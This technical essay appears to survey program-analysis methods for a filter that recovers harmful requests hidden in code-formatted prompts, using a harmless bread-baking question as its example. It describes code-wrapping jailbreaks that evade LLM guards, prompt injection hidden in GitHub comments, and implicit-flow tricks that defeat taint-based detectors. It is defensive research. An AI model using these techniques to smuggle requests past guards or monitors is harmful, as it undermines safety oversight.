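Some evidence suggests that exact recovery helps at this point. When Zhang and colleagues had the target model restate code-wrapped requests in plain language, guards blocked only 18–27% of the restatements, compared with 97.4% of the original plain requests. In a separate experiment with requests hidden in images, WildGuard blocked 92% of the attacks when it received an exact transcript of the image, but 42% when the model reworded the transcript without decoding anything. Images aren't code, and the rewording came from one small model. Still, rewording alone seems to remove much of what a guard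 responds to, and a static tool doesn't reword the text it recovers.

Judging the original prompt as well as the recovered text would be safer, but it raises the false positive rate. Zhang and colleagues tried this kind of double check with five guards and two target models, and all ten combinations refused more harmless requests.

### What tools for malicious scripts achieve

*Optimizing Away JavaScript Obfuscation* (Herrera, 2020) presents SAFE-Deobs, a tool for malware analysts and the existing tool most similar to this pipeline. It repeats six passes until the code stops changing. The passes fold constants using 59 rewriting rules, propagate constants, remove branches that can never run, replace trivial functions with their results, decode hexadecimal and Unicode escapes, and rename variables, but none of them decodes Base64.

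Four rounds of this reduced one malicious script from 475 lines to 12 and eliminated 211 of its 214 variables. The main thing left was a separately obfuscated command in PowerShell, another scripting language. The reductions were smaller across 28,285 scripts, where the average Halstead length (the count of operators and operands) fell by 28% and the number of functions by 26%.

A prompt filter couldn't use SAFE-Deobs unchanged, because some of its simplifications would destroy evidence. After propagating constants, it removes assignments that have become redundant. Nothing in the rye bread program uses `task` after line 6, so an optimising compiler would treat that line as dead code, and removing it would probably remove the hidden question too. A branch that never runs would probably also be removed, although a model will still read it. SAFE-Deobs can also rename every variable after an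 animal, which helps an analyst reading names like `1I11II` but not a filter looking for a variable called `rye_bread_recipe`.

*From Obfuscated to Obvious* (Zhou, Ying and colleagues, 2025) describes JSimplifier, a tool that adds two stages after static analysis. A sandbox runs pieces of code that static analysis can't resolve, and a language model gives the variables readable names. In tests largely on one sample program, static analysis alone handled 14 of 20 disguising techniques. Running code handled five more, including code that a program generates as it runs and loops that step through the program's statements in a scrambled order. The language model handled the last technique, which was giving variables meaningless names.

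Processing averaged about 9 seconds per script with or without the static stage, most of it fixed overhead such as loading and parsing. Adding the language model raised the average to 87 seconds. But on those 1,000 real malicious scripts, static analysis shortened the code by only 3.5% on the Halstead measure. The full system shortened it by 5.7%, compared with 88% on an artificial benchmark. Results on code disguised by researchers may therefore be a poor predictor of results on code from real attackers.

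Google's CASCADE targets one popular obfuscator, Obfuscator.IO, which moves a script's strings into a shuffled table and replaces each one with a calculation that looks it up. Older tools recognise the lookup code by fixed patterns, which break easily. Jiang and colleagues show that changing `while (!![])` to the equivalent `while (!false)` was enough to defeat one of these tools. CASCADE instead uses a language model, Gemini, to identify the lookup functions. It then runs those functions in a sandbox and uses constant propagation for the rest.

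On 11,736 test files, the tool recovered an average of 945 strings per file in 2.3 seconds, ranging from 0.8 seconds for the lightest disguise to 5.2 for the heaviest. Jiang and colleagues report a success rate of 98.9%, but they counted a file as a success if the tool finished within a minute without crashing, and they don't report how many of the strings were correct. Errors should be rare, since the program's own functions do the decoding and conventional tools generally preserve a program's meaning. In *JSDEOBSBENCH* (Chen, Jin and Lin, 2025), code from two rule-based deobfuscators rarely failed to run correctly, while code from six language models, all now old, failed 37% of the time on average.

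Split, escaped and conventionally encoded strings take little computation to recover, which is useful for a prompt filter. But most of these studies measure how tidy the code becomes, while a filter has to recover one particular sentence, in full and in the right order.

### Requests in names and comments

A prompt could also contain an empty function called `how_to_bake_rye_bread` and ask the model to complete it. Constant propagation would find nothing, because the request isn't a value in the program.

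*Beware of the Unexpected* (Chow, Schäfer and Pradel, 2023) presents Fluffy, a tool that uses names in taint analysis. It looks for flows that would surprise a programmer, such as a password ending up in a log file. Whether a variable holds a password is often clear only from its name. A standard taint tracker first treats every variable (or every parameter of a library function) as a source, which yields a large set of possible flows. A learned model then uses the names and any documentation to identify unexpected flows, and Fluffy reports only those that the tracker also found.

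Chow and colleagues tried four models for the second step. A small neural network trained on a few hundred hand-labelled examples did best for log files, with 90% precision and 94% recall. An existing set of hand-written name patterns had slightly higher recall, 97%, but only 79% precision. For four other kinds of flow, the network's F1 ranged from 76% to 97%. It did worst on flows into file paths, where the names were most varied. A simpler model that needed fewer than ten example names per category did nearly as well on most tasks. In a separate test, Fluffy detected 117 of 131 known vulnerabilities.

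The learned step is essential because only 58 of 272 randomly sampled flows into sensitive operations were unexpected. A tool that reported every flow would have been wrong 79% of the time.

A version for prompts could follow the same plan, with names and comments as additional sources and a guard as the learned model. But unlike the programmers behind Fluffy's data, who chose names to be understood, an attacker can choose names to mislead. A filter that trusted a variable called `cake_timer` could dismiss a correct alarm, so names should be able to raise suspicion but not lower it. Fluffy also skips single-letter names, but this is less of a loss because a name like `x` gives the model no information anyway.

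Static analysis can recover comments only if the parser keeps them. Cheng and colleagues use one such parser, Tree-sitter, to extract all comments, strings and names from a piece of code, along with blocks that look like decoys. Their tool then runs three checks, each requiring more computation than the last. It first applies simple rules to find obvious instructions and odd characters, then uses a small language model to measure how improbable the wording is. Finally, it replaces a suspicious item with something neutral and measures how much the small model's prediction changes.

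Averaged over six kinds of attack, the tool picked out the planted items with an F1 of 0.80, compared with 0.70 for the best of three earlier tools. Its lowest score, 0.66, was on attacks that mislead a model's reasoning about code. The tool also edits the items it flags, which damaged some clean code. Success on one set of programming problems fell by 6 points. Exact matches on a code completion test fell by 33 points, partly because that test counts any change of wording as a failure.

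A filter for hidden requests could reuse the extraction step, skip the editing, and pass the names and comments to a guard. This would leave clean code intact, but false alarms would remain a problem. A guard trained on conversations may flag "Kill all orphaned children" as harmful, though it is a normal comment in a program that manages processes. How often this would happen is unknown.

### Code that does not parse

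Every step after the first needs a syntax tree, and parsers often can't build one from real code. A standard parser rejected 18% of the 39,450 malicious scripts that Herrera collected. Of the 44,421 scripts in Zhou and colleagues' dataset, most of them disguised, one older deobfuscator processed 68% and another 32%.

JSimplifier processed all of them. It first repairs common faults, such as mixed character encodings, and tries another parser if one fails. But the perfect score is partly a result of how the team chose the malicious half of the collection. They started with 10.7 million scripts and discarded about a fifth because Meriyah, the parser JSimplifier uses to check its input, rejected them as corrupted or not JavaScript.

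Prompts are likely to be worse than malware in this respect, because malware has to run and a snippet in a prompt doesn't. The guard can't block everything that fails to parse, since people often paste in broken code to ask what is wrong with it. It can instead collect everything between quotation marks, which is crude but works on almost any input. This loses the order and labels of the strings, so the guard again has to judge all 200 strings in the file.

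A language model could also do the slicing. *SLICEMATE* (2025) uses language model agents that never build a dependence graph, and *SLICET5* (2025) includes incomplete snippets in its tests. But He and colleagues found that such slicers miss relevant statements, add irrelevant ones, and sometimes invent code. Their own model can't output tokens absent from the input, so it can't invent words, but it can still select the wrong ones. If a slicer omits a relevant statement, part of the request is lost, and if it adds an irrelevant one, the guard may judge an unrelated string.

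### Pseudocode and invented languages

Pseudocode has no fixed grammar, and an attacker can also make up a language and explain its rules in English. A more tolerant parser doesn't solve this, because the analysis also depends on what each operation does. This varies even among real languages. In JavaScript, as Zhou and colleagues note, `"5" + 3` gives the text "53", while `"5" - 3` gives the number 2. In an invented language, the prompt defines what `+` does.

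Taint labels can survive this better than constants can. Karimipour and colleagues faced a milder version of the problem with library functions whose code their tool could not inspect. Treating every result as tainted caused too many false alarms. Their solution was to treat the result as tainted only if one of the inputs was:

labels(f(y, z)) = labels(y) ∪ labels(z)

In their Java tests, this reduced recall very little. In a prompt with an unfamiliar function `mix(start, end)`, the rule would still show that "How", "do", "I", "bake" and "rye bread" reach the sink, although the tool couldn't determine their order.

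A guard might recognise a request from such a list of fragments, but most guards did badly on the code template that Zhang and colleagues tested, even though it left the words readable. If the unknown function is a decoder, the list will contain only encoded text, which is of little use to any guard. The only general fix is to have a language model translate the invented language into a real one, but the translation may contain errors that the static tool cannot detect.

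### A sink that exists only in prose

So far, a language model has identified the sink for the tool. This works when the prompt says "answer the question in `task`". It is harder when the prompt says "do what the second list describes", or never mentions the code and leaves the model to infer what the user wants. If the sink is misidentified, the tool can miss the whole request.

One safeguard is to also treat every value that the program computes but never uses as a sink. Such values have little purpose in an ordinary program, but one may be the main purpose of a code-formatted prompt. In the rye bread example, `task` is the only unused value. However, people often paste fragments of larger programs into a chat, and these contain many unused values too. They would cause false alarms, though fewer than if every variable were a sink. Nobody has measured how many fewer. An attacker who knew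 the rule could also add a line that prints `task`, so that it counts as used.

A prompt can also specify part of the computation in English, such as an instruction to read every other word of a string. A slicer can't follow the data through that step because no code statement performs it.

### Values that a loop builds up

Loops are a problem even when the code is flawless and the sink is obvious. This is a common way to join words in Python:

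```python
task = ""
for w in start:
    task = task + w + " "
```

When the program first reaches the loop, `task` is Const(""). After one pass it is Const("How "). These two values meet at the top of the loop, and because they differ, the merging rule makes `task` Unknown. Textbook constant propagation therefore handles `join` but fails on a loop that does the same job. The labels still show that the four words reach `task`, but not in what order.

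If the tool can determine how many times a loop will repeat, it can unroll the loop by writing out its body once per repetition. In this example, unrolling produces four copies of one line, and propagation then recovers "How do I bake " exactly. Because the recovered text is exact, unrolling adds no false alarms beyond those of the guard. The number of copies needs a limit, however, because it multiplies when loops are nested, and three nested loops of 100 repetitions each produce a million copies.

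Unrolling also fails when the number of repetitions depends on what the loop computes. Obfuscator.IO uses such a loop to rotate its table of strings until a sum matches a target value. Google's tool runs the loop instead of trying to predict the result.

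## Dynamic analysis: running the code and following the data

The simplest way to find out what a loop produces is to run it. A dynamic tool runs the code in a sandbox, an isolated environment where it can do no damage, and records the strings the code builds. Nobody seems to have published a test of this method on code-formatted prompts either, so the evidence again comes from research on malware and on flaws in ordinary software.

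### Reading off the value of `task`

In this version of the rye bread prompt, a loop picks the words out of a scrambled list:

```
1  words = ["bake", "How", "rye", "do", "bread", "I"]
2  task = ""
3  i = 1
4  while i != 6:
5      task = task + words[i] + " "
6      i = (i + 2) % 7
```

As before, the prompt includes one English instruction to answer the question in `task`. Constant propagation marks both `i` and `task` as Unknown. Unrolling the loop also fails, because a tool can find the number of passes only by tracking `i` through each one, which amounts to running the loop.

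To record what happens, the tool needs a modified interpreter that passes the result of each operation to a small extra routine called a hook. The hook gives the result the labels of all its inputs, using the same union rule as the static version. If the result is a string, the hook also logs it with its labels.

Suppose the six words have the labels 0 to 5, after their positions in the list, and the space has the label s. Each pass builds two strings, one without the final space and one with it. The log entries for the second of these are:

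```
pass   i   string                        labels
1      1   "How "                        1, s
2      3   "How do "                     1, 3, s
3      5   "How do I "                   1, 3, 5, s
4      0   "How do I bake "              0, 1, 3, 5, s
5      2   "How do I bake rye "          0, 1, 2, 3, 5, s
6      4   "How do I bake rye bread "    0, 1, 2, 3, 4, 5, s
```

The loop stops when `i` reaches 6, and the last entry is the value of `task`. During a run a variable has only one value at a time, so the tool never has to merge two values into Unknown.

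The recovered sentence is correct, but its labels are incomplete. The numbers on lines 3, 4 and 6 determine the order of the words, yet they don't appear in the log because, under the simple rule, an index doesn't pass its labels to the item it selects.

### From PowerShell malware to JavaScript packages

Malware analysts have long used runtime deobfuscation, which recovers hidden text by letting a script unpack itself. Much of this work concerns PowerShell, which has a command that runs a string as code. Attackers encode a whole script as a string and add code that decodes it just before passing it to that command. *PowerDrive* (Ugarte, Maiorca and colleagues, 2019) replaces the command with one that prints the string instead of running it, and repeats this until it finds no more layers of obfuscation.

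PowerDrive analysed 4,642 of the 5,079 malicious scripts collected, more than 95% of those that ran. Most were easy cases, since about 95% of the analysed scripts had a single layer of disguise, and in 89% of those the layer was an encoding, usually Base64. PowerDrive also doesn't trace variables. The rye bread loop never runs a string as code, so a tool that only watched for commands that do so would find nothing in it.

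In *PowerPeeler*, Li, Zhang and colleagues (2024) modified the PowerShell interpreter to record the result of each instruction that evaluates an expression. Their tool then writes the results back into the script in place of the disguised code. They selected 4,264 disguised script files and 381 disguised command lines from 1.7 million malicious samples. To measure correctness, they also disguised 100 scripts themselves, two or three times over, and checked each tool's output by hand.

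The table compares four of the tested tools. Invoke-Deobfuscation was the best of the static tools. A result counts as valid if the tool finished within two minutes and returned a syntactically correct script that differed from the original.

| Tool | Correct, of 100 scripts | Valid, of 4,264 files | Bytes per second |
|---|---|---|---|
| PowerPeeler | 95 | 3,421 | 14,887 |
| Invoke-Deobfuscation | 46 | 2,682 | 3,887 |
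| GPT-4 | 17 | 1,376 | 62 |
| PowerDrive | 0 | 150 | 45,836 |

PowerDrive scored zero mostly because it joins all the lines of a script into one, which breaks the syntax. GPT-4 is several generations old, so its results are weak evidence of what a current model could do. The comparison with the static tool is more informative. One test script, based on real malware, used a loop to decode a web address byte by byte. PowerPeeler recovered the address, while the other five deobfuscators and GPT-4 all failed.

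PowerPeeler's speed on long files is a poor guide to its speed on prompts. It processed the command lines, which average 1.8 KB and are closer to the length of a prompt, at only 137 bytes per second, or about 13 seconds for an average sample. Much of that time is probably fixed overhead, and a prompt filter wouldn't need to rewrite the script afterwards, but few chat users would wait 13 seconds for a safety check.

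One of Li and colleagues' smaller experiments closely resembles a filter that recovers text and passes it to a guard. Windows lets PowerShell send code to antivirus software before running it, but PowerShell sends only whole blocks of code, so a suspicious word that the script assembles from pieces can get through. The researchers disguised a script that Microsoft Defender recognised in ten ways. Defender allowed all ten versions in ordinary PowerShell but, without modification, blocked all ten when it received PowerPeeler's log of results. However, the test used only one underlying script, and Defender only had to match known strings, which is much easier than judging whether a question is harmful.

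PowerPeeler records values but doesn't label them. *Mystra* (Zhang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) presents Shar, a tool that tracks labels in JavaScript and Python. Shar keeps the labels in a "shadow" machine that runs beside the interpreter and updates with every operation. It can't observe the inner workings of some built-in functions, so the researchers wrote rules for them in a small language, also called Mystra. For example, the rule for JavaScript's Base64 decoder passes the input's labels to the result.

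Shar detected 471 of 493 known flaws in JavaScript packages (95.5%) and raised no false alarms on 141 packages whose developers had fixed the flaw. On a benchmark of small packages, it increased the average running time by a factor of 1.85, from 68.5 to 126.4 milliseconds. Three older tools, which rewrite a program's source before running it, slowed the same benchmark by factors of 29 to 51. Shar may slow heavier computation more, but most code in prompts is short.

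Sixteen of the 22 misses happened because a label disappeared when a library took a labelled value apart. Zhang, Liu and colleagues describe string splitting as the main cause of missed flows. This is worrying for prompts, where disguises often depend on splitting and rejoining strings. The packages also came from developers who had made mistakes and had no reason to evade a tracker. Shar ignores implicit flows, partly because another tool that tracked them slowed programs by a factor of 36.7.

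### What it costs to track implicit flows

Staicu, Schoepe and colleagues (2019), in *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript*, measured the overhead and benefits of tracking implicit flows. They distinguish observable implicit flows from hidden ones. In Denning and Denning's example, a program sets `y` to 0 only if `x` is 0. If the assignment runs, the flow is observable because a tracker can mark `y`. If it doesn't run, `y` still reveals information about `x`, but the flow is hidden because the tracker has no assignment to act on.

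The researchers ran 56 JavaScript programs with known security problems. They measured how far labels spread with a simple ratio:

label creep ratio = assignments of labelled values / all assignments

According to their summary, including implicit flows increased this ratio by over 40%. In their detailed results, the ratio was 45.4% lower when tracking only explicit flows than when tracking both explicit and observable flows. Adding observable flows therefore increased the ratio by about 83%, so "over 40%" may understate the increase. Tracking hidden flows as well added almost nothing.

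The tracker also had to process more operations, over 2.5 times as many in browser scripts and in programs that a malicious input can stall with a slow text search. The increase was small in programs vulnerable to code injection. These operation counts don't translate directly into running time.

For the 46 server-side programs, tracking explicit flows was enough to detect every problem, and the additional alarms from tracking implicit flows were all false. One of these programs checks whether a database query is a function and, if it is, stores some constants. Tracking implicit flows gives the constants the query's label, even though whoever sent the query can't change them.

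The other ten programs were browser scripts that identify visitors or find out which sites they have been to. Their leaks were implicit, so a tracker limited to explicit flows missed them. These were also the only programs in the study whose authors might have acted in bad faith.

### When the adversary writes the program

In 2008, Cavallaro, Saxena and Sekar had argued in *On the Limits of Information Flow Techniques for Malware Analysis and Containment* that this pattern was to be expected. In trusted software, an attacker controls the input but not the code. If data from the network directly determines which file a program opens, the developer probably didn't intend it, and an alarm is justified. Such a program may contain implicit flows, but the attacker can't add more, whereas malware authors can because they write the code.

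Their main example is a detector for bots, programs that obey commands from a remote attacker. The detector marks everything that arrives from the network and raises an alarm when marked data reaches a sensitive system call. A bot can copy one bit of a command, `y`, without ever assigning `y` to anything:

```python
if y == 1:
    x = 1
else:
    x = 0
```

A loop around this code can copy a command of any length. The detector can respond by marking every variable assigned inside a branch that tests marked data, but this produces false alarms on harmless programs. For example, a weather application might read one byte from the network that indicates whether text or an image is coming, and choose a file name accordingly. The detector would then mark the file name, and the application would look like a bot.

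Even then, the bot can still get around the detector:

```python
x = 0
z = 0
if y == 1:
    x = 1
else:
    z = 1
if x == 0:
    w = 0
if z == 0:
    w = 1
```

If `y` is 1, the program sets `x` to 1 in a branch that depends on `y`, so the detector marks `x`. But `z` is still 0 and unmarked, so the test of `z` succeeds and sets `w` to 1 without marking it. If `y` is 0, the detector marks `z` instead, and the test of the unmarked `x` succeeds and sets `w` to 0. Either way, `w` ends up equal to `y` but has no mark.

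The information passes through the assignment that didn't happen, which a monitor of the run can't observe. To be safe, the detector has to assume that anything the program writes may depend on anything it has read. Then "selectivity is lost", as Cavallaro and colleagues put it, and the detector must flag every program that uses the network, which it could do without tracking any data.

They were writing about compiled programs, where it is very hard to work out what an untaken branch would have changed. In a Python snippet, the untaken branch is visible in the source, so a combined static and dynamic tool could mark `w` in this example. It would still have to mark the weather application's file name.

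### A string without its history

Most of this argument matters little for a prompt filter. The bot detector depended on labels because opening a file is innocent unless somebody else chose the file, but a guard can judge a question mainly by its words. If the rye bread program copied `task` into a second variable letter by letter, using branches like the ones above, the labels would disappear, but the log would still record "How do I bake rye bread" as the second variable's value.

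Marking everything is also less of a problem, since a prompt's flows don't show whether the request is harmful anyway.

Some of the other attacks from 2008 don't carry over. In one, a malicious browser plug-in changed a value just after the tracker checked its label. In a small test program on a four-core machine, this worked 60–80% of the time. A snippet running alone in a sandbox has no browser to exploit this way.

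An attacker can still make labels useless for narrowing down the strings that a guard has to check. If branches can strip a string of its labels, the filter can't safely ignore unlabelled strings. It has to judge everything in the log, and a run can produce many more strings than the source contains. The rye bread loop built twelve strings, ten of them fragments. Discarding any string that is part of a longer one leaves only the full question there, but this won't always work so well. A program can print its words one at a time without ever joining them, so the filter should also keep the printed output in order.

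Checking more strings can also add false alarms. In the double check by Zhang and colleagues, the guards caused all the extra refusals, since the models behind them refused fewer harmless requests than before. But those guards judged a model's paraphrase, and exact strings from a sandbox might cause fewer false alarms or more.

### Code that was never meant to run

The PowerShell tools rely on the fact that malware has to run. Li and colleagues left out scripts with syntax errors and scripts that needed outside input. They also removed 1,185 scripts that only defined functions, because those contained nothing to execute. All three kinds of code are normal in a chat. A user may paste in a function and ask what it would return for a certain list. The function call is then described only in English, and a language model would have to write it in code before a sandbox could run anything.

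Other requests never involve a computation. *DoubtProbe* (2026) gives an example in which a harmful aim is hidden in what looks like an ordinary code-completion task. The harm would be in the code that the model adds, so running the unfinished version would probably recover nothing. A reduced version of the defence, which only audited the prompt's meaning, judged it benign and answered. The full system also reconstructs the request and compares the result with the original. It blocked this prompt because the original contained several concrete blocks of code, while the reconstruction was a generic description of a completion task. This is a single case, but it suggests that a failure to recover the request can be a useful signal.

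When PowerPeeler can't obtain a result, such as a file from a server, it substitutes a placeholder and keeps running. Any expression that includes the placeholder becomes a placeholder too. If the prompt never defined the word "rye", this rule would replace the whole question with a placeholder. A prompt filter would do better to keep the known parts and mark the gap, as in "How do I bake [missing] bread". The missing word may be in the English part of the prompt, where the model will find it.

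Code can also behave differently in a sandbox. Ugarte and colleagues found instructions to pause in 50.8% of their scripts, a common way to outlast a time-limited analysis. PowerDrive deletes these instructions, and PowerPeeler breaks out of a loop if the loop's values haven't changed after ten passes. A prompt's author has an additional advantage because the model only reads the code, so it may skip over a pause or an enormous loop that can use up the sandbox's time. If the result depends on the date, a random number or a file, the sandbox and the model may also use different values and follow different branches.

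Running the code in every prompt means executing strangers' programs on the operator's own machines. The malware researchers accepted some of this risk. PowerDrive ran the decoded scripts to collect the files they downloaded, and 18 of the web addresses it found were still active. Li and colleagues were more cautious. Their tool blocked downloads and commands such as those that restart the computer, and they reset the virtual machine after every sample.

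A prompt filter can be much stricter and block both the network and the file system without losing any of the request, because a model in a plain chat can't use them either. An interpreter that supports only numbers, strings and lists would be enough to run the rye bread loop, and would have no command for deleting a file. It would still need limits on time and memory.

### Where the interpreter and the model part ways

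Even running the code perfectly shows only what Python computes, while the model also reads the comments. *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) examines a related problem on the code-sharing site GitHub, where people hide instructions to AI agents in places such as HTML comments, which browsers don't display. The researchers replayed 43 real attacks against five models. Four never carried out an injected instruction, but the fifth, the smallest and fastest, complied with eight. Stripping the comments removed the threat entirely, but would also remove every legitimate hidden instruction.

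A sandboxed run also ignores comments, so the filter doesn't check them, but the model still receives them. An attacker could write code that builds "How do I bake rye bread" and add a comment that changes the question. The filter would approve the bread question without checking the changed one.

Harder code widens the gap. Lam and colleagues ran all their altered programs to confirm that the results hadn't changed. Models' accuracy in predicting those results still fell by 6.5 percentage points on average when the researchers inserted code that does nothing, and by 14 points when they combined this with new names and more convoluted conditions. Plausible but false hints reduced Claude 3.5 Sonnet's accuracy on one set of problems from 73.8% to 41.8%.

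These models are old, but later ones have some of the same weakness. *How Robustly do LLMs Understand Execution Semantics?* (2026) found that changing a program's inputs, or rewriting the program without changing its meaning, generally lowered accuracy a little but lowered GPT-5.2's substantially. Models also did much worse at predicting when a program would fail with an error. *Teaching LLMs Program Semantics via Symbolic Execution Traces* (2026) tested whether models could tell that a program violated a stated property. Even after special training, accuracy fell from 91.7% on programs of up to 25 lines to 57.1% on those of 101 to 200 lines.

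Many of these mistakes are harmless for a safety filter. If the sandbox recovers a dangerous question that the model would have misread, the filter blocks an attack that would probably have failed anyway. The serious mistakes occur when the run produces something innocent, or crashes, but the model still gets a harmful request from the names, the comments or a guess about an undefined function. A harmful string from the sandbox can justify blocking a prompt, but an innocent one is not enough to clear it, which is another reason to judge the original prompt as well.

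Training on recorded runs, which helped Maimon and colleagues' small models, may make prediction mistakes rarer. *Evaluating Exact Output and Checkpoint-State Prediction in Real Programs* cites a similar experiment in which an 8-billion-parameter model's accuracy rose from 44.6% to 73.9%, although its score on practical software repairs barely changed. Even a model that simulated Python perfectly, and so got the same value for `task` as the sandbox, would still read the comments.

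## Symbolic execution, and what no filter can decide

A sandbox can't run a function when the prompt describes its argument only in English. Symbolic execution treats the argument as an unknown and works out what the code would build for each possible value. Nobody seems to have published a test of this technique on code-formatted prompts.

### One snippet, two questions

In this variant of the running example, a number decides which of two questions the code builds:

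```
1  def build(n):
2      verb = "bake"
3      item = "rye bread"
4      if 2 * n + 3 == 17:
5          verb = "wash"
6          item = "a wool coat"
7      return "How do I " + verb + " " + item
```

The English part asks the model to answer the question that `build` returns when given the number of days in a week, so the argument, 7, appears nowhere in the prompt. Constant propagation would merge the two paths after line 6 and mark `verb` and `item` as Unknown.

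A symbolic executor tracks each execution path separately. *A Survey of Symbolic Execution Techniques* (Baldoni, Coppa and colleagues, 2016) describes the executor's state as a triple (stmt, σ, π), where stmt is the next statement, σ is a store that gives each variable a value or an expression, and π is the path condition, which lists what must be true of the unknowns for the program to have taken this path. An assignment changes σ. A branch on a condition e makes two copies of the state, one with π ∧ e and the other with π ∧ ¬e.

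For `build`, the tool represents the argument as α:

```
start       σ: n = α                                        π: true
line 3      σ: n = α, verb = "bake", item = "rye bread"     π: true
line 4      the state splits in two
              if true,  go to line 5                        π: 2α + 3 = 17
              if false, go to line 7                        π: 2α + 3 ≠ 17
```

It then follows each copy to the end and passes the conditions to a constraint solver, a program that looks for values that make a formula true or proves that none exist. This is usually an SMT solver such as Z3, which can handle numbers, arrays and strings as well as true-or-false statements.

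| Path condition | A value that satisfies it | String returned |
|---|---|---|
| 2α + 3 = 17 | 7 | How do I wash a wool coat |
| 2α + 3 ≠ 17 | 0 | How do I bake rye bread |

A filter can send both strings to a guard without determining which one the model will build. This risks a false alarm over a string on a path that would never run.

The solver can rule out some of these paths. The condition `n * (n + 1) % 2 == 1` is never true for a whole number, since either `n` or `n + 1` is even. People who disguise programs use such conditions, called opaque predicates, to add branches that never run. *Symbolic Execution in Practice* (Bailey and Nicholas, 2025) describes a tool that starts from a suspicious region of code and works backwards to prove that no run can reach it. A prompt filter should still check branches that never run, since the model reads them.

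### When a prompt needs this at all

As Baldoni and colleagues explain, a symbol represents a value that the code does not determine, such as a function's argument or data from outside. The earlier rye bread snippets have no such values, so symbolic execution would follow a single path through each and return the same string as the sandbox. Most hidden requests are probably like this, because an attacker who wants a particular answer must ensure the model can rebuild a particular question.

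Even `build` doesn't need symbolic execution if a small language model adds the call `build(7)` for the sandbox to run. If a later message supplies the missing value, the filter can run again then.

In the remaining cases, the filter can't predict the value. A prompt might tell the model to pick a number, or describe the number so vaguely that two models would read it differently. The code might also check for signs of a sandbox and build something harmless if it finds them. Malware often does this. Bailey and Nicholas describe a tool that uses symbolic execution to find the values that lead past such checks, then patches the program to take the hidden path.

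Concolic execution, which combines concrete and symbolic execution, is a practical compromise. The tool runs `build(0)`, gets the bread question, and records that the run depended on 2α + 3 ≠ 17. It then reverses that condition, the solver returns 7, and a second run gives the coat question. Every string the tool reports comes from a real run, so the program can actually produce it. The tool can still miss strings, because a new input doesn't always take the path that the solver predicted. Baldoni and colleagues cite a study in which inputs departed from the predicted path more than 60% of the time.

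*ConcoLixir* (2026) names two difficulties that Python adds: symbolic tracking can be lost partway through a program, and the tool can't analyze what happens inside some library calls. A call to Python's Base64 decoder is one of these, because compiled C code does the decoding.

### How paths multiply

One branch on an unknown value gives two paths, and Bailey and Nicholas give the general rule that n branches can lead to as many as 2ⁿ. Suppose a snippet short enough to fit on one screen chooses each word of a sentence with a separate test on a separate unknown, and the tool needs a millisecond per path. Ten branches produce 1,024 paths, which take about a second to analyze. Twenty produce 1,048,576, which take over 17 minutes, and 30 produce more than a billion, which take about 12 days.

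The number of paths is much smaller when the branches depend on each other. If thirty tests each check whether `n` equals a different number, at most one can succeed, so only 31 paths are possible. A solver can discard the rest as it goes.

Loops can be worse than branches. A loop that repeats `n` times has a separate path for every value of `n`, so the number of paths has no limit. Tools usually stop after a fixed number of repetitions and miss anything the program builds later.

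Another remedy is to merge similar states. The tool could store the result of the thirty-branch snippet in very little memory, as thirty slots with two possible words in each. But a guard judges sentences, and the slots still describe about a billion of them. Merging therefore leaves the hardest part to the guard, which must work out from the word lists whether any of those sentences is harmful.

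### Why strings are hard for solvers

The condition in `build` is simple arithmetic. Conditions on unknown strings can be far harder, even when they are very short. Suppose a branch runs only if

x + "a" = "b" + x

for some unknown string x. A common method compares the two sides from the left. The string can't be empty, because "a" and "b" differ, so it must start with "b". The solver writes x as "b" + y and removes the first "b" from both sides, which leaves

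y + "a" = "b" + y

This is the original equation with the unknown renamed. A solver that doesn't record earlier equations will repeat the step forever. Counting letters shows that there is no solution, because the left side always has one more "a" than the right.

Eisenhofer, Seiser and colleagues (2026), in *On Solving String Equations via Powers and Parikh Images*, add a general form of this counting to a solver for cases where its other rules fail. The solver still isn't guaranteed to stop when an equation has no solution. According to their paper, equations with long repeats, or with unknowns that depend on each other, remain very hard for the leading solvers.

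The theory of these equations is also unfinished. Makanin proved in 1977 that an algorithm can always decide whether an equation built from letters and unknown strings has a solution. The problem is NP-hard, so a fast method for every case would also give fast methods for every problem in NP, the class of problems whose solutions are quick to check. Yonemoto (2026), in *Quadratic Word Equations with a Linear Side*, notes that nobody has settled whether the problem itself belongs to NP, even when each unknown appears at most twice. For a narrower class, Yonemoto proved that every solvable equation has a solution path of manageable length, but the bound grows with the twelfth power of the equation's size.

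Ordinary Python conditions go beyond plain equations. In *A Survey on String Constraint Solving*, Amadini (2020) lists the decidability of string equations combined with arithmetic on lengths as unknown. *Undecidability of a Theory of Strings, Linear Arithmetic over Length* (2016) proved that no algorithm can decide every case if the theory also includes conversion between strings and numbers. Beginners use both features, as `len(s)` and `int(s)`. Even for conditions requiring that one string not contain another, decidability was an open problem until 2025, when Havlena, Hečko and colleagues proved it for strings restricted by simple patterns.

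A limit on string length makes these problems decidable, since a computer could in principle try every string. But there are 141 trillion strings of ten lower-case letters, so trying them all is seldom practical. Solvers instead use more efficient methods and a time limit. *Hybrid Concolic Testing with Large Language Models for Guided Path Exploration* (2026) points out that if the solver runs out of time on a possible path, a testing tool has to abandon it and may miss a bug.

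A prompt filter can often avoid this loss. In `build`, both questions are complete before the solver runs, and the solver only checks whether a path is possible. If the solver runs out of time, the filter can keep the path and have the guard check the string, which may add a false alarm but avoids missing a possible path.

This doesn't work when the text itself depends on the unknown. If the code shifts every letter of a string by `n` places, the store holds only an expression containing α. The tool can try all 26 possible shifts, but a scheme with an eight-letter key has about 209 billion possible keys. The model has the same problem unless the key is in the conversation or easy to guess, and a filter that reads the conversation might find it there.

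### A model in place of the solver

Before a solver can work on a condition, a tool has to translate it into the solver's formal language, which is often impossible for strings, library calls and unusual data structures. AutoExe (later AutoBug), the tool in Li, Meng and Duck's *Large Language Model powered Symbolic Execution* (2025), skips the translation. It splits a program into paths and represents each path as a slice of ordinary code instead of a formula. It then gives a language model one short slice at a time and asks whether a stated property holds at the end of the slice.

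According to the paper, analyzing real programs accurately often takes larger models that accept longer inputs, and these need enterprise-grade hardware. Splitting the code into shorter pieces should reduce that need. The method also needs no solver, because the model reads the code directly. That would suit prompts, where the code may be in pseudocode or an invented language.

Using a language model in place of a solver gives up soundness. Baldoni and colleagues call an analysis sound if it finds every unsafe input. A solver proves that a formula has no solution before reporting so, whereas a language model may be wrong when it reports that a property holds, and its answer doesn't show whether it is. The paper acknowledges that language models are inherently probabilistic. The number of paths can also still grow exponentially. Slicing shortens the code on each path, but thirty independent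 branches could still require about a billion queries to the model.

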